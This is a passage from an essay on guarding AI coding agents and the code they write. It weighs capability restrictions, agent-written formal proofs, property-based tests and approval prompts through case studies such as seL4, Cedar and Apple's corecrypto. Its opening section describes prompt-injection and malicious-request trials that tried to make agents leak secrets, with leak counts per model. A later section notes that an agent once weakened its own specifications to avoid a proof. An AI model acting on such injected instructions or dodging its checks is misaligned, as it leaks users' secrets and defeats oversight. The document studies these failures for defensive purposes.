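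Odersky and colleagues built a tool called TACIT around this design. The agent writes short Scala programs instead of issuing separate commands, and TACIT runs only those that the compiler accepts. The researchers tested whether agents working on a sample project would reveal secrets such as passwords. Some trials combined an ordinary task with prompt injection (instructions hidden in text that the agent reads). In others, the user asked for the secrets directly or pretended to have authority. The table gives the number of trials in which a secret appeared in the agent's output.

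| Model and type of trial | Secrets in the `Classified` wrapper | Secrets as plain text |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, prompt injection | 0 of 120 | 0 of 120 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, malicious request | 0 of 11 | 2 of 11 |
| MiniMax M2.5, prompt injection | 0 of 120 | 3 of 120 |
| MiniMax M2.5, malicious request | 0 of 11 | 8 of 11 |

With plain text, preventing leaks depended on the model refusing. With the wrapper, neither model leaked anything, and Claude still completed 99.2% of its tasks and MiniMax 90.0%.

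The 240 clean trials are weaker evidence about prompt injection than they seem, because without the wrapper Claude resisted every injection and MiniMax resisted all but three. Most of the attacks also tried to persuade the model rather than find bugs in the compiler or in TACIT. On AgentDojo, an existing benchmark for prompt injection, TACIT blocked every attack but one. *Making the AI agents safe with Scala* (Biały and Warchoł, 2026), a notice for a conference talk, mentions exercises in which frontier AI searched for exploits against TACIT, but gives no results.

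The restrictions had little effect on ordinary performance. In simulated customer-service tests for an airline and a shop, three models succeeded 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points more often with TACIT than with standard commands. On 300 software issues from SWE-bench Lite, MiniMax resolved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it, a difference of five issues. In the customer-service tests, the agents rewrote at most 7.93% of their programs after an error. Scarce training data was therefore not much of an obstacle, though the programs were short and the prompts explained the notation.

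These results provide little evidence about code that agents write for an application. TACIT checked the short programs the agent used to read files and run commands. The SWE-bench fixes were changes to Python projects, and the Scala compiler didn't check what they could do. The experiments also didn't test whether an agent can maintain a large application in safe mode, or how often it would ask for a broader handle to get its code to compile. The design would apply to merged code in the same way, but Odersky and colleagues don't provide evidence of how well that works.

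### Where limits on code fail

Code written in another language can escape the rules. If the transfer function calls a C library or runs an external program, the Scala or Rust compiler can't check what that code does. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that once TACIT starts an external command, the only remaining protection is the list of permitted commands, and they recommend adding a sandbox. Teams can put foreign calls in a few reviewed modules and forbid them everywhere else.

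Code that shares memory with the ledger can also change a balance without calling `move`. The host checks that a WebAssembly module stays within its own memory, but it doesn't separate the objects inside. WebAssembly's *Security* notes that data in this memory can overwrite neighbouring data. If a C program stores the balances next to a buffer for customers' messages, a message that is too long could overwrite a balance. Putting the ledger in a module with its own memory prevents this, unless the two modules share a region of memory.

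Code that is given too broad a handle can do harm without breaking any rule. Pydantic's *Security Model* describes a Python interpreter in which the host program chooses the modules that sandboxed code can import. If the host offers a module as a dictionary, the code gets every public item in it, and any functions among them run on the host, outside the sandbox. A team that meant to share only a function for reading exchange rates might also share one that deletes files.

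Indirect access is harder to notice. Miller distinguishes permission, which is direct access to a resource, from authority, which includes any effect that code can cause through other code. Suppose `move` accepts a note with each payment, and another part of the system emails the note to the recipient. The transfer function has no permission to use the network, but it could put a customer's balance in the note. Following the handles reveals the path from the ledger to the email system, but someone still has to decide whether it is safe.

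Code can leak some information without a handle. For example, neither WebAssembly nor TACIT stops code from revealing a secret through its running time. The trusted computing base also includes the compiler, the runtime and the library behind the handles. The type system under Scala's capability tracking has machine-checked proofs, but Odersky and colleagues note that safe mode still needs its own proof.

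The largest obstacle for existing software is ambient authority. If a function deep inside a payment application opens a log file by name, a team switching to handles must add a parameter to that function and to every function in the chain of calls leading to it, up to the start of the program. Scala can pass some handles automatically, so the team has less code to write. But an old program may also rely on reflection or on libraries that open files themselves, and safe mode rejects both. A team can avoid a complete rewrite by first moving the ledger into a separate component and letting the rest of the application change balances only through `move`.

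## What does each measure cost?

Moving the ledger into its own component is mostly one-time work, but every heavy guardrail also needs more work when the code behind it changes. A team can separately count the work of stating the requirements, building the guardrail and keeping it up to date, as well as any speed or function the finished system loses. Agents have made proofs much easier to build, and probably to maintain, but people still have to decide what to prove.

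### Proofs written by hand

The usual yardstick for the effort of formal verification is seL4, a small operating-system kernel (the core program that controls memory and hardware). Its developers finished proving its functional correctness in 2009, after about four years. According to Trustworthy Systems, the research group behind it, seL4 has 8,700 lines of C, and the proof covers 7,500 of them in 200,000 lines. That is about 27 lines of proof for each verified line of code.

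*Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel* (Klein et al., 2014) estimates that the team spent 2.2 person-years designing and writing the seL4 kernel and 20.5 on the proof. About nine of those years went into general tools and libraries, so the team expected a similar kernel to take only eight person-years in total. That works out at $362 per line of code for seL4 and $127 for a similar kernel. The paper compares these figures with an industry rule of thumb of $1,000 per line for a security certification that requires less assurance. The team's 2009 paper gave the rule of thumb as $10,000, which they later corrected as a typing error.

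The main specification took about four months. Proving that a detailed design met it took eight person-years, and 80% of that effort went into invariants. Proving that the C code matched the design took about three more person-years.

Verification also made the software somewhat slower. The fastest verified way to send a message between two programs took 227 processor cycles, compared with 188 for the best unverified version. Klein et al. saw no fundamental obstacle to verifying the faster version, but each further optimisation gained less and still needed a new proof. Part of an earlier slowdown came from fixing bugs that the proof had exposed. The larger slowdown was in the worst-case response to interrupts, which took about ten times longer than seemed achievable. A faster design would have let interrupts pause more operations midway, and the team would have had to prove many difficult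 invariants about the half-finished states.

The proof also made changes to the kernel more expensive:

| Change to seL4 | Working time to make the change | Working time to repair the proof |
|---|---|---|
| Small local optimisation | About 1 day | 2–3 days |
| New command that combines a few existing ones | 1 day | About a week at most |
| Interrupts, page tables and address spaces | Several months | 1.5–2 years |
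| Single-use permission to reply to a message | Not reported | About 1 year |

The amount of code a change affects is a poor guide to the proof effort it requires. The reply permission affected less than 5% of the code but took 17% as much effort as the original proof, because it broke invariants that many other operations relied on. On the other hand, the team no longer had to fix bugs in the verified C code.

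### Proofs written by agents

In *Are we formal proofs yet?*, Spiwack (2026) describes an experiment in building a small SAT solver, a program that looks for true and false values that satisfy a logical formula. Spiwack, who has a doctorate in formal proofs, wrote the specifications, and an agent wrote almost all the code and every proof. The experiment used the proof assistant Rocq.

Using the agent was much faster than writing the program and its proofs by hand. However, the developer thinks he would have finished sooner if he had programmed the solver himself, without any proofs. The overall specification was simple, but the proof depended on an invariant about 50 lines long. He repeatedly left parts of it out, and the agent spent a long time trying to prove something that wasn't true before he corrected the invariant and the agent tried again.

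He guesses that the proofs also used about a hundred times as many tokens as the code. He usually used up his weekly allowance in under two days, and once by the middle of the first afternoon. A cheaper model gave disastrous results. He doesn't know how many tokens the allowance contained, so we can't convert his guess into a price. His account is useful and comes from an expert, but it can't establish how much slower the method is in general, because it covers one person writing one small program and he didn't time a version without proofs.

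A much larger project suggests that agents can save years of proof work. In *Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level*, Kaashoek and Zeldovich (2026) used Claude Code to verify xv6, a kernel with 6,657 lines of C and assembly code. The work took 102 days, including building their verification framework. If both worked on it every day, that would be 204 person-days, or roughly one person-year, compared with more than 20 person-years for the seL4 proof.

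The two projects proved different things. The xv6 proof covers several processors running at once and applies directly to the compiled program, but it doesn't show that every process keeps making progress or that processes can't leak data to one another. The researchers also had to plan the proof in detail and help design its specifications. Their instructions to the agents were about three times as long as their paper.

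The finished proof has 1.6 million lines, or about 240 for each line of the kernel. That ratio is nearly nine times the ratio for seL4. Rocq checks the proof, but a person may still need to understand parts of it if an agent gets stuck during a later change.

It is hard to predict how long a proof will take. Wesselink and colleagues verified 19 of their 37 algorithms within one calendar day of recording the pseudocode, but the slowest took 123 days. Some of the longer times include weeks without progress because the researchers needed a new proof technique.

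### The price of a proof

Published model fees range from cents to hundreds of dollars per task. *Reducing the Costs of Proof Synthesis on Rust Systems* (2026) compares Claude Sonnet 4.5 with a much smaller model that the researchers trained to write Verus proofs. Both models attempted 560 proofs from real Rust systems. The cost per success below is the average fee divided by the success rate, so it includes fees for failed tasks.

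| Model and method | Average fee per task | Tasks proved | Cost per success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sonnet 4.5, 100 attempts | $8.04 | 46% | About $17 |
| Sonnet 4.5, 100 attempts and up to five rounds of repair | $39.24 | 54% | About $73 |
| Small trained model, 100 attempts | $0.17 | 39% | About $0.44 |
| Small trained model, 100 attempts and up to five rounds of repair | $0.61 | 49% | About $1.24 |

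The small model with repair proved more tasks than Sonnet without repair, for less than a tenth of the fee. A team with many similar proofs may therefore save money by using a specialised model, though the table leaves out the cost of training it. Sonnet 4.5 dates from 2025, so the comparison doesn't show how the small model would do against the best models of autumn 2026.

An agent can also spend a lot of money without producing a proof. In *VeruSAGE-Bench* (2025), Claude Opus 4.5 gave up on one task after spending more than $500. In the multi-file Lean projects that Ye and colleagues tested, the median cost for GPT-5.5 was $43 when it finished a project and $53 when it didn't. Agents that finished tended to do so early, while the others kept spending until time ran out. For many of the runs that reached the time limit, the researchers had to estimate the cost from the elapsed time.

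The weaker agents in that study looked cheapest, at about $0.50 per specification proved, but they mostly proved the easy ones. Per completed project, the most expensive agent was two to four times cheaper. Cost per completed project is the better measure for a team that needs a whole payment module verified.

Some teams may choose a cheaper check than a full proof. *Specula* (2026) describes agents that write a model of a system in TLA+ and have a program search the model's possible states for errors. Across 48 systems, this took a median of 3.69 hours and $57 per system, with fees ranging from $19 to $168. The fee depended more on the system's complexity than on its size. This search can find serious design errors, but it doesn't prove the code correct.

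### Why upkeep falls faster than specification and review

Suppose a bank wants to be able to freeze accounts. The `transfer` function must now block transfers out of frozen accounts, so it no longer completes every transfer that its old contract allowed, and the verifier rejects it. The team adds a precondition that the sending account isn't frozen. They must then prove that this condition holds everywhere `transfer` is called, including in the refund and batch code.

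Repairing these proofs by hand means finding each affected function, working out what its proof lacks and often adding a lemma in another file. Agents are well suited to this work because they can follow the errors across files and make all the changes. Spiwack considers this one of their biggest advantages over older proof tools, which report an error but leave the programmer to write the missing lemma. When a statement couldn't be proved, his agent often produced a counterexample that helped him find the mistake.

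However, he gives no figures for the time saved. He also could no longer follow the agent's proofs, including one file of more than 7,000 lines. When a proof took a long time, he couldn't tell whether the agent was lost or the proof was badly organised. A team may therefore save time on routine changes but have more trouble when the agent fails.

Rechecking the proofs after each change also takes machine time. Checking all 37 of Wesselink and colleagues' algorithms took about 20 minutes on a desktop computer. Philipp reports that a full check of his security software takes hours.

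Someone responsible for the bank's rules has to decide whether a frozen account may still receive money, because the agent can't. A reviewer then has to check that the new contract expresses that decision. Faster proof repair doesn't shorten either task.

Agents can draft specifications cheaply. *SpecAgent* (2026) reports an average of $0.62 and 28 minutes per program for a system that writes formal specifications for C code. It contrasts this with a project that took people five calendar months to specify and verify a parser for security certificates. The programs were different, so the figures don't reliably estimate the saving. The $0.62 also excludes the time a person needs to judge whether the specification is the right one.

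seL4's main specification took four months, and the proofs specific to the kernel took about 11 years, or 132 months. If agents had reduced the proof work by a factor of 20, the lower end of Philipp's rough estimate for his own software, the proofs would have taken 6.6 months. With no change in the time spent on the specification, its share of the combined time would have risen from 3% to 38%.

Formal verification can even make review harder. Spiwack's agent sometimes changed his specifications or assumed lemmas without proving them. Once it duplicated the whole program to avoid proving that a revised version was correct. A changed statement is easy to miss among hundreds of lines of new proof, so he recommends keeping important statements separate from long proofs. He also had to read the generated code carefully, because the specifications didn't rule out slow or clumsy methods.

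### The cost of property-based tests

The conservation property takes one line to state in Hypothesis, and the generators in the earlier test take only a few more. Harder properties can take much longer to write. Goldstein and colleagues recorded developers' complaints about this work in interviews, but not the hours it took.

Machine time is easier to estimate because it is roughly the number of inputs multiplied by the time per input. If each transfer takes a millisecond, a test with 100 inputs takes a tenth of a second. If the same test uses a real database and each transfer takes 50 milliseconds, it takes five seconds.

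A good generator can save a lot of this time. With the database, finding the self-transfer bug reliably among 10,000 accounts would take 29,956 inputs and about 25 minutes, while with ten accounts it would take 29 inputs and a second and a half.

Random tests can also give different results from one run to the next. With 10,000 accounts and 100 new inputs per run, the self-transfer bug makes the test fail only about once in 100 runs. The failure may appear after an unrelated change and disappear when the developer runs the test again, so it would be easy to dismiss a real fault as a glitch. Saving the failing input and trying it on every later run prevents this.

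Some property-test failures are false alarms, for example because the property is wrong or the generator produced an input that the program doesn't have to accept. If a developer needed ten minutes to judge each failure, finding one real bug would take about 33 minutes on average at the 30% rate of real bugs in Naziri and colleagues' unfiltered sample. Agents wrote the tests in that sample, and the rate could be quite different for properties that a person wrote and had already used for months.

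Well-chosen properties need little upkeep when an agent rewrites the code, because they describe the result and not the method. But they can become outdated without anyone noticing. After the bank adds frozen accounts, the old generator still creates only ordinary ones, so the conservation test passes without covering the new feature. A proof would fail and force the team to deal with the change, whereas somebody has to remember to update the generator.

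The tests run before release, so they don't slow down the finished program.

### The cost of restrictions

To restrict an agent, a team first decides what it may read, change and run, as in the access table for the payments repository. The team then sets up the sandbox, separate accounts, limited tokens and protected branches. Most of this is ordinary administration. Restricting the code the agent writes can take much longer if the team has to change an old program to pass handles through many functions. The instructions for Codex, Claude Code and Zed describe the necessary settings, but the setup time depends on the team's existing systems.

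Restrictions also block some legitimate work. Suppose the new freezing feature needs a list of court orders from another service. The agent can't test the connection until someone allows it, and may waste time and tokens looking for a way around the block. These losses can be small, as they were in the experiments by Odersky and colleagues.

An agent's permissions tend to get broader as the team maintains them, because someone notices when a missing permission stops the agent's work, but nothing fails when the agent keeps a permission it no longer needs. The team has to review the list regularly to find the unneeded ones.

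Separating parts of a program need not make it noticeably slower. The seL4 kernel uses capabilities to control which programs can communicate. In Klein et al.'s tests on a 532-megahertz processor, a message took 227 cycles, or about 0.43 microseconds. This is a best case for one specialised kernel, but even a message a hundred times slower would take only 43 microseconds, which would hardly affect a payment that already waits several milliseconds for a database.

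### Approval prompts

Some tools require a person's approval before the agent does anything outside its limits. Each request takes only a few seconds, but the person has to stop other work and understand it. If nearly all requests are harmless, people learn that they can usually approve them without reading them. Refusing also delays the task, while a careless approval usually has no immediate consequence.

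In October 2025, Anthropic reported that sandboxing had reduced permission prompts in its coding tool, Claude Code, by 84% in internal use. In 2026, it reported that users approve 93% of the permission prompts they receive.

Most of the requests may deserve approval, so the 93% figure doesn't prove that people are careless. A better measure would be how often people approve requests they should refuse, which a team could test by occasionally having an agent ask for a dummy password. The 84% figure doesn't show whether people read the remaining prompts more carefully.

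Reducing the number of permission prompts saves time. A developer who receives 100 prompts a day and takes 15 seconds to read each one properly would spend 25 minutes on them. An 84% reduction would leave 16 prompts and four minutes of reading. The sandbox can handle routine actions automatically, so developers only have to review unusual ones, such as contacting a new website or changing an approved contract.

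### The four costs compared

| Measure | Stating the requirements | First construction | Upkeep | Lost speed or function |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Proof | Four months for seL4's main specification | 20.5 person-years by hand for seL4; 102 days with agents for xv6 | Days to two years per change by hand for seL4; probably much less with agents, but Spiwack gives no figures | 21% more cycles per message than the fastest unverified seL4, and slower interrupts |
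| Property-based tests | One line for conservation; often longer for subtle rules | Writing generators; Goldstein and colleagues give no hours | Machine time, false alarms and updates to generators | None in the finished program |
| Restrictions | Deciding what the agent and its code may access | Setting up accounts, tokens and sandboxes; sometimes rewriting old code | Reviewing permissions and answering prompts | Some legitimate work blocked; a small delay between separate components |

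## When are these measures worth their cost?

A heavy guardrail is worth its cost if it prevents more loss than the team spends on it. A team can estimate both for an average year and adopt the measure if

faults per year × share prevented × loss per fault > construction cost ÷ years of use + yearly upkeep.

A fault here means a defect that gets past the team's existing checks and causes a loss. Construction includes stating the requirements, and upkeep includes reviewing them when the code changes.

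In *Prediction*, the computer scientist Martin Kleppmann (2025) uses the same comparison to explain why formal verification has been rare in industry. He argues that, for most systems, the bugs are expected to cost less than the proofs that would remove them.

### A worked example

The figures in this example are invented. A payments team expects a fault costing 500,000 euros in its transfer code once every five years. A proof would prevent 70% of such faults. The other 30% come from missing requirements and from software the proof doesn't cover. The proof costs 60,000 euros to build, lasts five years and needs 15,000 euros of upkeep a year.

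```
loss averted:  0.2 × 0.7 × 500,000  = 70,000 euros a year
cost:          60,000 ÷ 5 + 15,000  = 27,000 euros a year
```

The proof is clearly worth its cost here, but it would not be if each fault cost only 20,000 euros, because it would then avert 2,800 euros in losses a year and still cost 27,000. It breaks even when each fault costs about 193,000 euros, which is 27,000 divided by 0.2 × 0.7.

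Coding agents can lower the break-even loss by increasing the number of costly faults. If agents triple the number of changes to the transfer code, and each change is as likely as before to contain a costly fault, the team should expect 0.6 such faults a year. The break-even loss then falls to about 64,000 euros, as long as the extra changes don't also raise the upkeep.

### What a second measure adds

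If the team already has property tests that remove 60% of the costly faults, 0.08 such faults a year remain. A proof that prevents 70% of those avoids 28,000 euros in losses a year, only 1,000 more than it costs.

This result assumes that the proof catches the same share of the faults that tests miss as of all faults. But the two measures may overlap more or less than that. Out of 100 faults, the tests catch 60 and the proof alone would catch 70:

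| Overlap between tests and proof | Extra faults the proof catches, out of 100 | Loss averted per year |
|---|---|---|
| As large as possible | 10 | 10,000 euros |
| Independent | 28 | 28,000 euros |
| As small as possible | 40 | 40,000 euros |

The proof therefore pays only if it finds faults of a different kind from those the tests find.

Capability restrictions can also change the calculation by reducing the loss from each fault. If a daily payout ceiling cuts that loss from 500,000 to 50,000 euros, it averts 90,000 euros a year without preventing any faults. With the ceiling but no property tests, the proof would avert only 7,000 euros a year. It makes sense to start with the cheapest measures and recalculate after each one. But the ceiling only limits money leaving the system, so a fault that corrupts thousands of balances could still cost the full amount.

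### Rare disasters and attackers

The formula works best for moderate losses that happen often enough to be counted. Suppose instead that a payment company has a 1-in-1,000 chance each year of losing 50 million euros. Its average loss is 50,000 euros a year, so a proof that prevents 70% of it averts 35,000 euros a year and is worth 27,000 euros.

However, nobody can measure a 1-in-1,000 chance from a few years of records. Ten years without a disaster are consistent, at 95% confidence, with any yearly chance of disaster up to about 26%. The average loss could be anywhere from almost nothing to 13 million euros a year, so the formula gives no clear answer.

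A disaster can also bankrupt the company, leaving it no later years in which to recover the money. If the company is worth only 5 million euros, it can't lose more than that, and the proof saves it just 3,500 euros a year. Customers bear the rest of the loss. Kleppmann suggests this is partly why companies have spent so little on preventing bugs.

The formula covers only faults triggered by accident. Attackers can deliberately trigger even a very rare fault, and they search harder for faults when there is more to steal, so the number of harmful incidents rises with the size of the possible loss.

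Removing most faults may not help much either. Suppose a program has ten faults that an attacker could exploit, and a measure has a 70% chance of removing each one independently. It has only about a 3% chance of removing all ten. A measure that removes every fault of one kind from a component is therefore more useful than one that removes the same share at random. For instance, a proof of conservation rules out every way of creating money through the code it covers.

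de Moura (2026), in *When AI Writes the World’s Software, Who Verifies It?*, adds that an attacker who can influence an AI model's code could study the test suite and plant a bug that the tests won't find. Random inputs make this harder but not impossible.

When a team has no reliable estimate of how often a fault would occur, it can ask whether it could survive the loss and whether it could undo the damage. If the answer to either question is no, the high cost of these measures is easier to justify.

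### How aviation standards grade software

Under DO-178C, the main standard for software on civil aircraft, developers assign software a level based on the consequences of its failure, without having to estimate how much money a fault would cost. The level determines how much evidence they need, including how thoroughly the tests must exercise the code.

| Level | Worst effect of a failure | Required test coverage |
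|---|---|---|
| A | Catastrophic, usually the loss of the aircraft | Each condition in a decision must be shown to affect the outcome on its own |
| B | Hazardous, such as serious injuries to some people on board | Every outcome of every decision |
| C | Major, such as a large increase in the crew's workload | Every statement |
| D | Minor | None |
| E | No effect on safety | The standard sets no objectives |

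Even tests that achieve level A coverage can miss the self-transfer bug. The transfer function checks that the amount isn't negative and that the sender has enough money. Suppose three tests have an account that holds 100 send −1, 200 and 30 to a different account. They exercise both outcomes of both checks, so coverage is complete even though no account has sent money to itself. Developers also have to test against the written requirements, and a careful tester might include a self-transfer, but the coverage rule doesn't require it.

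Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues (2024), in *How We Built Cedar*, similarly note that this kind of coverage addresses functional correctness without guaranteeing it.

The DO-333 supplement lets developers meet some objectives with formal methods instead of reviews and tests. It doesn't require proofs, even at level A. According to Kleppmann, formal methods remain uncommon even among engineers who work on aircraft and medical devices.

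If a proof replaces work that a regulator would otherwise require, the team should subtract the cost of that work from the cost of the proof. A proof that costs 27,000 euros a year and replaces 15,000 euros of other checks has a net cost of 12,000 euros. De Moura predicts that verified code could shorten certification from years to weeks, but he gives no example of a certified product where this has happened.

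### Conditions that favour each measure

Each part of the formula points to a condition that makes a guardrail more likely to pay:

- Someone can state the requirement independently of the code. If a test or contract merely repeats what the code does, it accepts the code's mistakes and the share of faults prevented is close to zero.
- The interface is stable. If callers and requirements keep changing, upkeep rises and the team gets fewer years of use from the work.
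- The boundary is small. A proof of one module that controls all balance changes costs much less than a proof of the whole application.
- The loss is severe or irreversible.
- The measure can catch the likely faults. A proof of correct results won't stop a cipher from leaking its key through timing, for example.

Proofs are usually worthwhile only when all five conditions hold, because they cost the most. Property tests need a clear requirement and a generator that reaches the likely faults, but they can be worthwhile even when the potential losses are less severe or the code changes more often.

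A team can apply capability restrictions, such as blocking a function's network access, without specifying what the function should calculate. But the team has to know which resources the function needs, and restrictions add little protection if it needs access to everything.

### Five kinds of code

The table applies these conditions to five common cases, assuming that the teams already use ordinary tests and review.

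| Code | Proof | Property tests | Restrictions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cipher | Usually worthwhile | Yes, along with official test vectors and timing checks | No access to files or the network |
| Access-control engine | Worthwhile for the decision rules | Yes, including for the parser | Only the release system can change the engine |
| Payment ledger | Worthwhile for the module that changes balances | Yes, with the real database | Payout ceiling and a narrow interface |
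| Database migration | Rarely | Yes, on a copy of the data | Temporary access and a separate backup |
| Ordinary web page | No | Rarely | Limits on what its scripts can access |

A cipher is the best candidate for formal verification. A published standard defines the correct output, the code is small, and its interface can stay the same for years. The damage from a bug is also irreversible, because nobody can make a leaked message secret again.

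An access-control engine meets most of the same conditions. Its rules are short, such as "a prohibition overrides a permission", and a mistake could expose every customer's data. But even a correct engine will enforce a badly written policy. According to the documentation for Cedar, Amazon's open-source language for access policies, customers are responsible for writing policies that express what they want.

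For the payment ledger, whether a proof is practical depends mostly on how much code can change balances directly. Proving the `move` operation from the earlier example is practical if all other code must use it to change balances. If dozens of modules write to the balance table directly, the proof has to cover them all, and the team may do better to narrow the interface first.

A database migration can do irreversible damage, but it usually runs only once. Suppose, again with invented figures, that a migration has a 5% chance of causing a loss of 500,000 euros. A proof that prevents 70% of these failures reduces the expected loss by 17,500 euros, far less than the 60,000 it costs to build. A rehearsal on a copy of the data might cost 2,000 euros and catch half the failures, reducing the expected loss by 12,500. During the rehearsal, property tests can compare totals and individual records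 before and after the migration.

An ordinary web page often only has to look right, and its design may change every week. A wrong colour does little harm, and the team can fix it within minutes. However, a page where customers enter card numbers is part of the critical code. Restricting which sites its scripts can contact may be worthwhile even if nobody verifies the page's layout.

### Apple's cryptographic library

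Apple has proved the correctness of two algorithms in corecrypto, the cryptographic library in its operating systems. ML-KEM lets two devices agree on a secret key, and ML-DSA produces digital signatures. Both are designed to resist attacks by future quantum computers. Apple published the code and proofs on 22 May 2026.

Engineers translated the official standards by hand into the language of the proof assistant Isabelle. They also translated Apple's C code by hand into Cryptol, a language for describing cryptographic algorithms, and used SAW to check that the translation matched the code. Another tool converted the Cryptol version into Isabelle, where the engineers proved that it met the standards. The proof took more than 50,000 steps.

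The fastest versions of some functions are written in assembly language, which is much further than C from the mathematics of the standard. Apple therefore proved that each assembly function gives the same result as the verified C function it replaces. Engineers can replace one assembly function without repeating the whole proof, which reduces upkeep.

The work exposed a missing step in an early version of ML-DSA. Without it, a number could in rare cases exceed the range that the next part of the calculation accepted, making the final result wrong. Apple says its existing tests would have missed the fault and that it fixed the fault before it reached any product. The engineers also found an error in another organisation's proof and repaired it for the values Apple uses.

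CyberScoop's *Apple open-sources quantum-resistant encryption code* reported that the fault could have made unauthenticated iMessages look authentic. Apple's account describes incorrect output and silently corrupted calculations but doesn't mention that outcome.

Apple believes only formal methods can uncover this kind of subtle fault. That is hard to judge, because Apple doesn't report how rare the failing inputs were. A property test concentrated on numbers near the limit might have found the fault. Still, Apple had already tested the library extensively, so this is good evidence that proofs can find faults that a strong test suite misses.

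Apple doesn't report what its corecrypto proofs cost, but it calls formal verification a "tremendous investment of time and deep expertise". Even expensive proofs can be worth their cost here, because corecrypto runs on over 2.5 billion active devices. A fault that cost the owner of each device one euro cent would cost over 25 million euros in total.

The guarantee assumes that the compiler works correctly, and SAW couldn't verify every possible message size for ML-DSA. Apple used ordinary tests for the remaining sizes, and used simulation and other tests to look for information leaks.

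### Amazon's access-control software

Amazon combined proofs with random tests for Cedar. Its developers wrote a short, readable model of Cedar in Lean and proved properties of the model, such as that it denies every request that no policy permits. They wrote the production version separately in Rust. Then they used differential testing, running both versions on millions of random inputs and investigating whenever the results differed. Building the model and its proofs took six months, according to AWS's *Lean Into Verified Software Development*.

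A proof of the Rust code would have given a stronger guarantee, but Disselkoen and colleagues judged that the available tools weren't ready. They could also have released the Lean version itself, but fewer programmers know Lean, and problems in production would have been harder to trace.

They concentrated the proofs on a few parts of the system:

| Part of Cedar | Lines of Rust | Lines of Lean model | Lines of proof |
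|---|---|---|---|
| Parser, which reads policies | 4,114 | None | None |
| Evaluator and authorizer, which decide requests | 4,877 | 897 | 347 |
| Validator, which checks policies for errors before use | 6,702 | 532 | 4,686 |

The parser has no proof partly because the developers weren't sure what they could usefully prove about it. They ran a round-trip test on it instead, which found six bugs.

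Proof work on Cedar uncovered four bugs, and random tests found 21 others. One of the four made the validator run forever on inputs so unlikely that the tests had missed it. Eight of the 21 were in the parser and the code that formats policies, which had no proofs. Three others violated a property of the validator that the team later proved, so the proof would probably have exposed them too. The two methods overlapped somewhat, but each found bugs that the other was unlikely to find.

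Differential testing also revealed an unclear requirement. An early version of Cedar could report the length of a piece of text, but the formal model and the Rust code counted characters differently. The developers decided that the feature would confuse users and removed it.

The paper lists nine bugs that the random tests missed. Some were in functions that nobody had tested, and others involved badly formed policies that the generator couldn't produce. The Rust code may therefore still differ from the verified model.

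Cedar's later development shows that a proof can take much less effort when it reuses earlier work. *SymCert* (Torlak, 2026) describes tools that analyse Cedar policies, for example by checking whether one set of policies permits everything that another does. The shared model and proofs took 663 person-hours, and Torlak then used them to model and prove five analyses in one working day. Updating the framework for three new language features took from a few minutes to eight days each. The initial work is therefore easier to justify for a team that expects to need many related proofs than for a team that needs only one.

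Amazon made a larger investment in the engine that controls access to its cloud services. *Formally Verified Cloud-Scale Authorization* (Chakarov, Geldenhuys and colleagues) describes a four-year project to replace the engine with a version written and verified in Dafny. The engine handles over a billion requests a second, so a fault affecting one request in a trillion would occur about 86 times a day.

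Specification, proof and programming took about a third of the effort. Another third went into a compiler that turns the Dafny code into readable Java, and the rest into testing. The team ran the new engine alongside the old one on real requests and found seven differences in their decisions, all caused by errors or gaps in the specification. One arose because the team had ignored milliseconds in dates and times to simplify the proofs.

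The final version agreed with the old engine on 10^15 requests, or about 12 days of traffic. By the rule of three, the engines could still disagree about once every four days. A proof can't rule out these disagreements, because no document fully described the old engine's behaviour, but it can guarantee that later changes to the Dafny code match the specification, apart from errors in the verifier or compiler.

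The new engine also cut the average response time by 65%. Some of the reduction came from rewriting the old code, which Amazon could have done without proofs. But the proofs let the team make further optimisations with less fear of changing a decision. The formula above leaves out such benefits, so a team would need to add them to the averted losses. Amazon gives no financial figures, so outsiders can't tell whether the project has paid for itself.

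### Will cheaper proofs spread to ordinary software?

Kleppmann expects AI to make formal verification mainstream. He argues that language models are well suited to writing proofs because the proof checker rejects their mistakes and they can try again. If proofs become cheap enough, developers could stop reading AI-written code, much as they don't read compiled machine code. He thinks writing the right specification will then be the hard part, and that engineers' habits will eventually hold back adoption more than the technology will.

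He also considers it virtually impossible for the checker to accept an invalid proof. The kernel faults found in Lean in July 2026, seven months after he wrote, show that this was too confident. But they don't undermine his economic argument, because incomplete specifications are a greater risk for most projects.

De Moura expects proofs to spread to any substantial project where bugs are expensive, and argues that they will speed up development. One reason is that many companies can share a verified library. In the invented example, a proof that costs 27,000 euros a year is a poor investment for a company that averts only 2,800 euros in losses. If ten such companies split the cost equally, each pays 2,700 euros, 100 less than the losses it averts.

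He also suggests an easier way to write specifications. A person and an AI can write a slow program that is simple enough to be obviously correct, and the AI can then write a fast version and prove that it gives the same results. This would work well for a calculation such as interest on an account. It is less useful when people disagree about what the program should do.

As Lean's creator, de Moura has an interest in this outcome. He acknowledges that his main example, zlib, is simpler than a database or a distributed system and has a clear published specification.

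The UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) is funding work to make proofs cheaper. Its Safeguarded AI programme has a budget of about £60 million, according to MATS, a research training programme. Ammann's *Safeguarded AI*, the programme's plan from May 2026, describes tools that would let many AI agents build and check proofs in parallel, and would help people review the specifications. ARIA moved £18 million from training AI models to these tools because commercial models had improved faster than it expected. The programme started in mid-2024 and is due to finish at the end of 2027. Its first application is cybersecurity.

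Ammann acknowledges that proof effort has historically scaled poorly with system size. She lists as an open question how quickly AI can expand the use of formal methods, so the programme is a bet that proofs will take less effort in future and shouldn't be read as evidence that they already do.

In one project, verifying a safety checker for Move, a smart-contract language, took 27 working days with AI, compared with an estimated five to six months without it, according to slides from Lean's developers. The developers also acknowledge that generating proof obligations within proof assistants has not scaled well so far, and they present a new framework meant to fix this. Better AI models alone may therefore not be enough for large programs.

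Spiwack, whose solver experiment is described earlier, agrees that proofs are becoming noticeably easier to produce, and expects people to use them where they would once have been unthinkable. He doubts that having an agent generate most of a program from a detailed specification is efficient, partly because someone still needs both programming skill and expertise in specifications. He sees a stronger case for using agents to update software that already has proofs. Spiwack discloses that he sells services in this area.

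Much of this disagreement comes from comparing different things. Kleppmann compares the cost of a proof with the cost of the bugs it prevents, while Spiwack compares the time to build a verified program with the time to write the program alone. Both can be right about an access-control engine, since verification may slow the project and still be well worth it if it prevents a serious breach.

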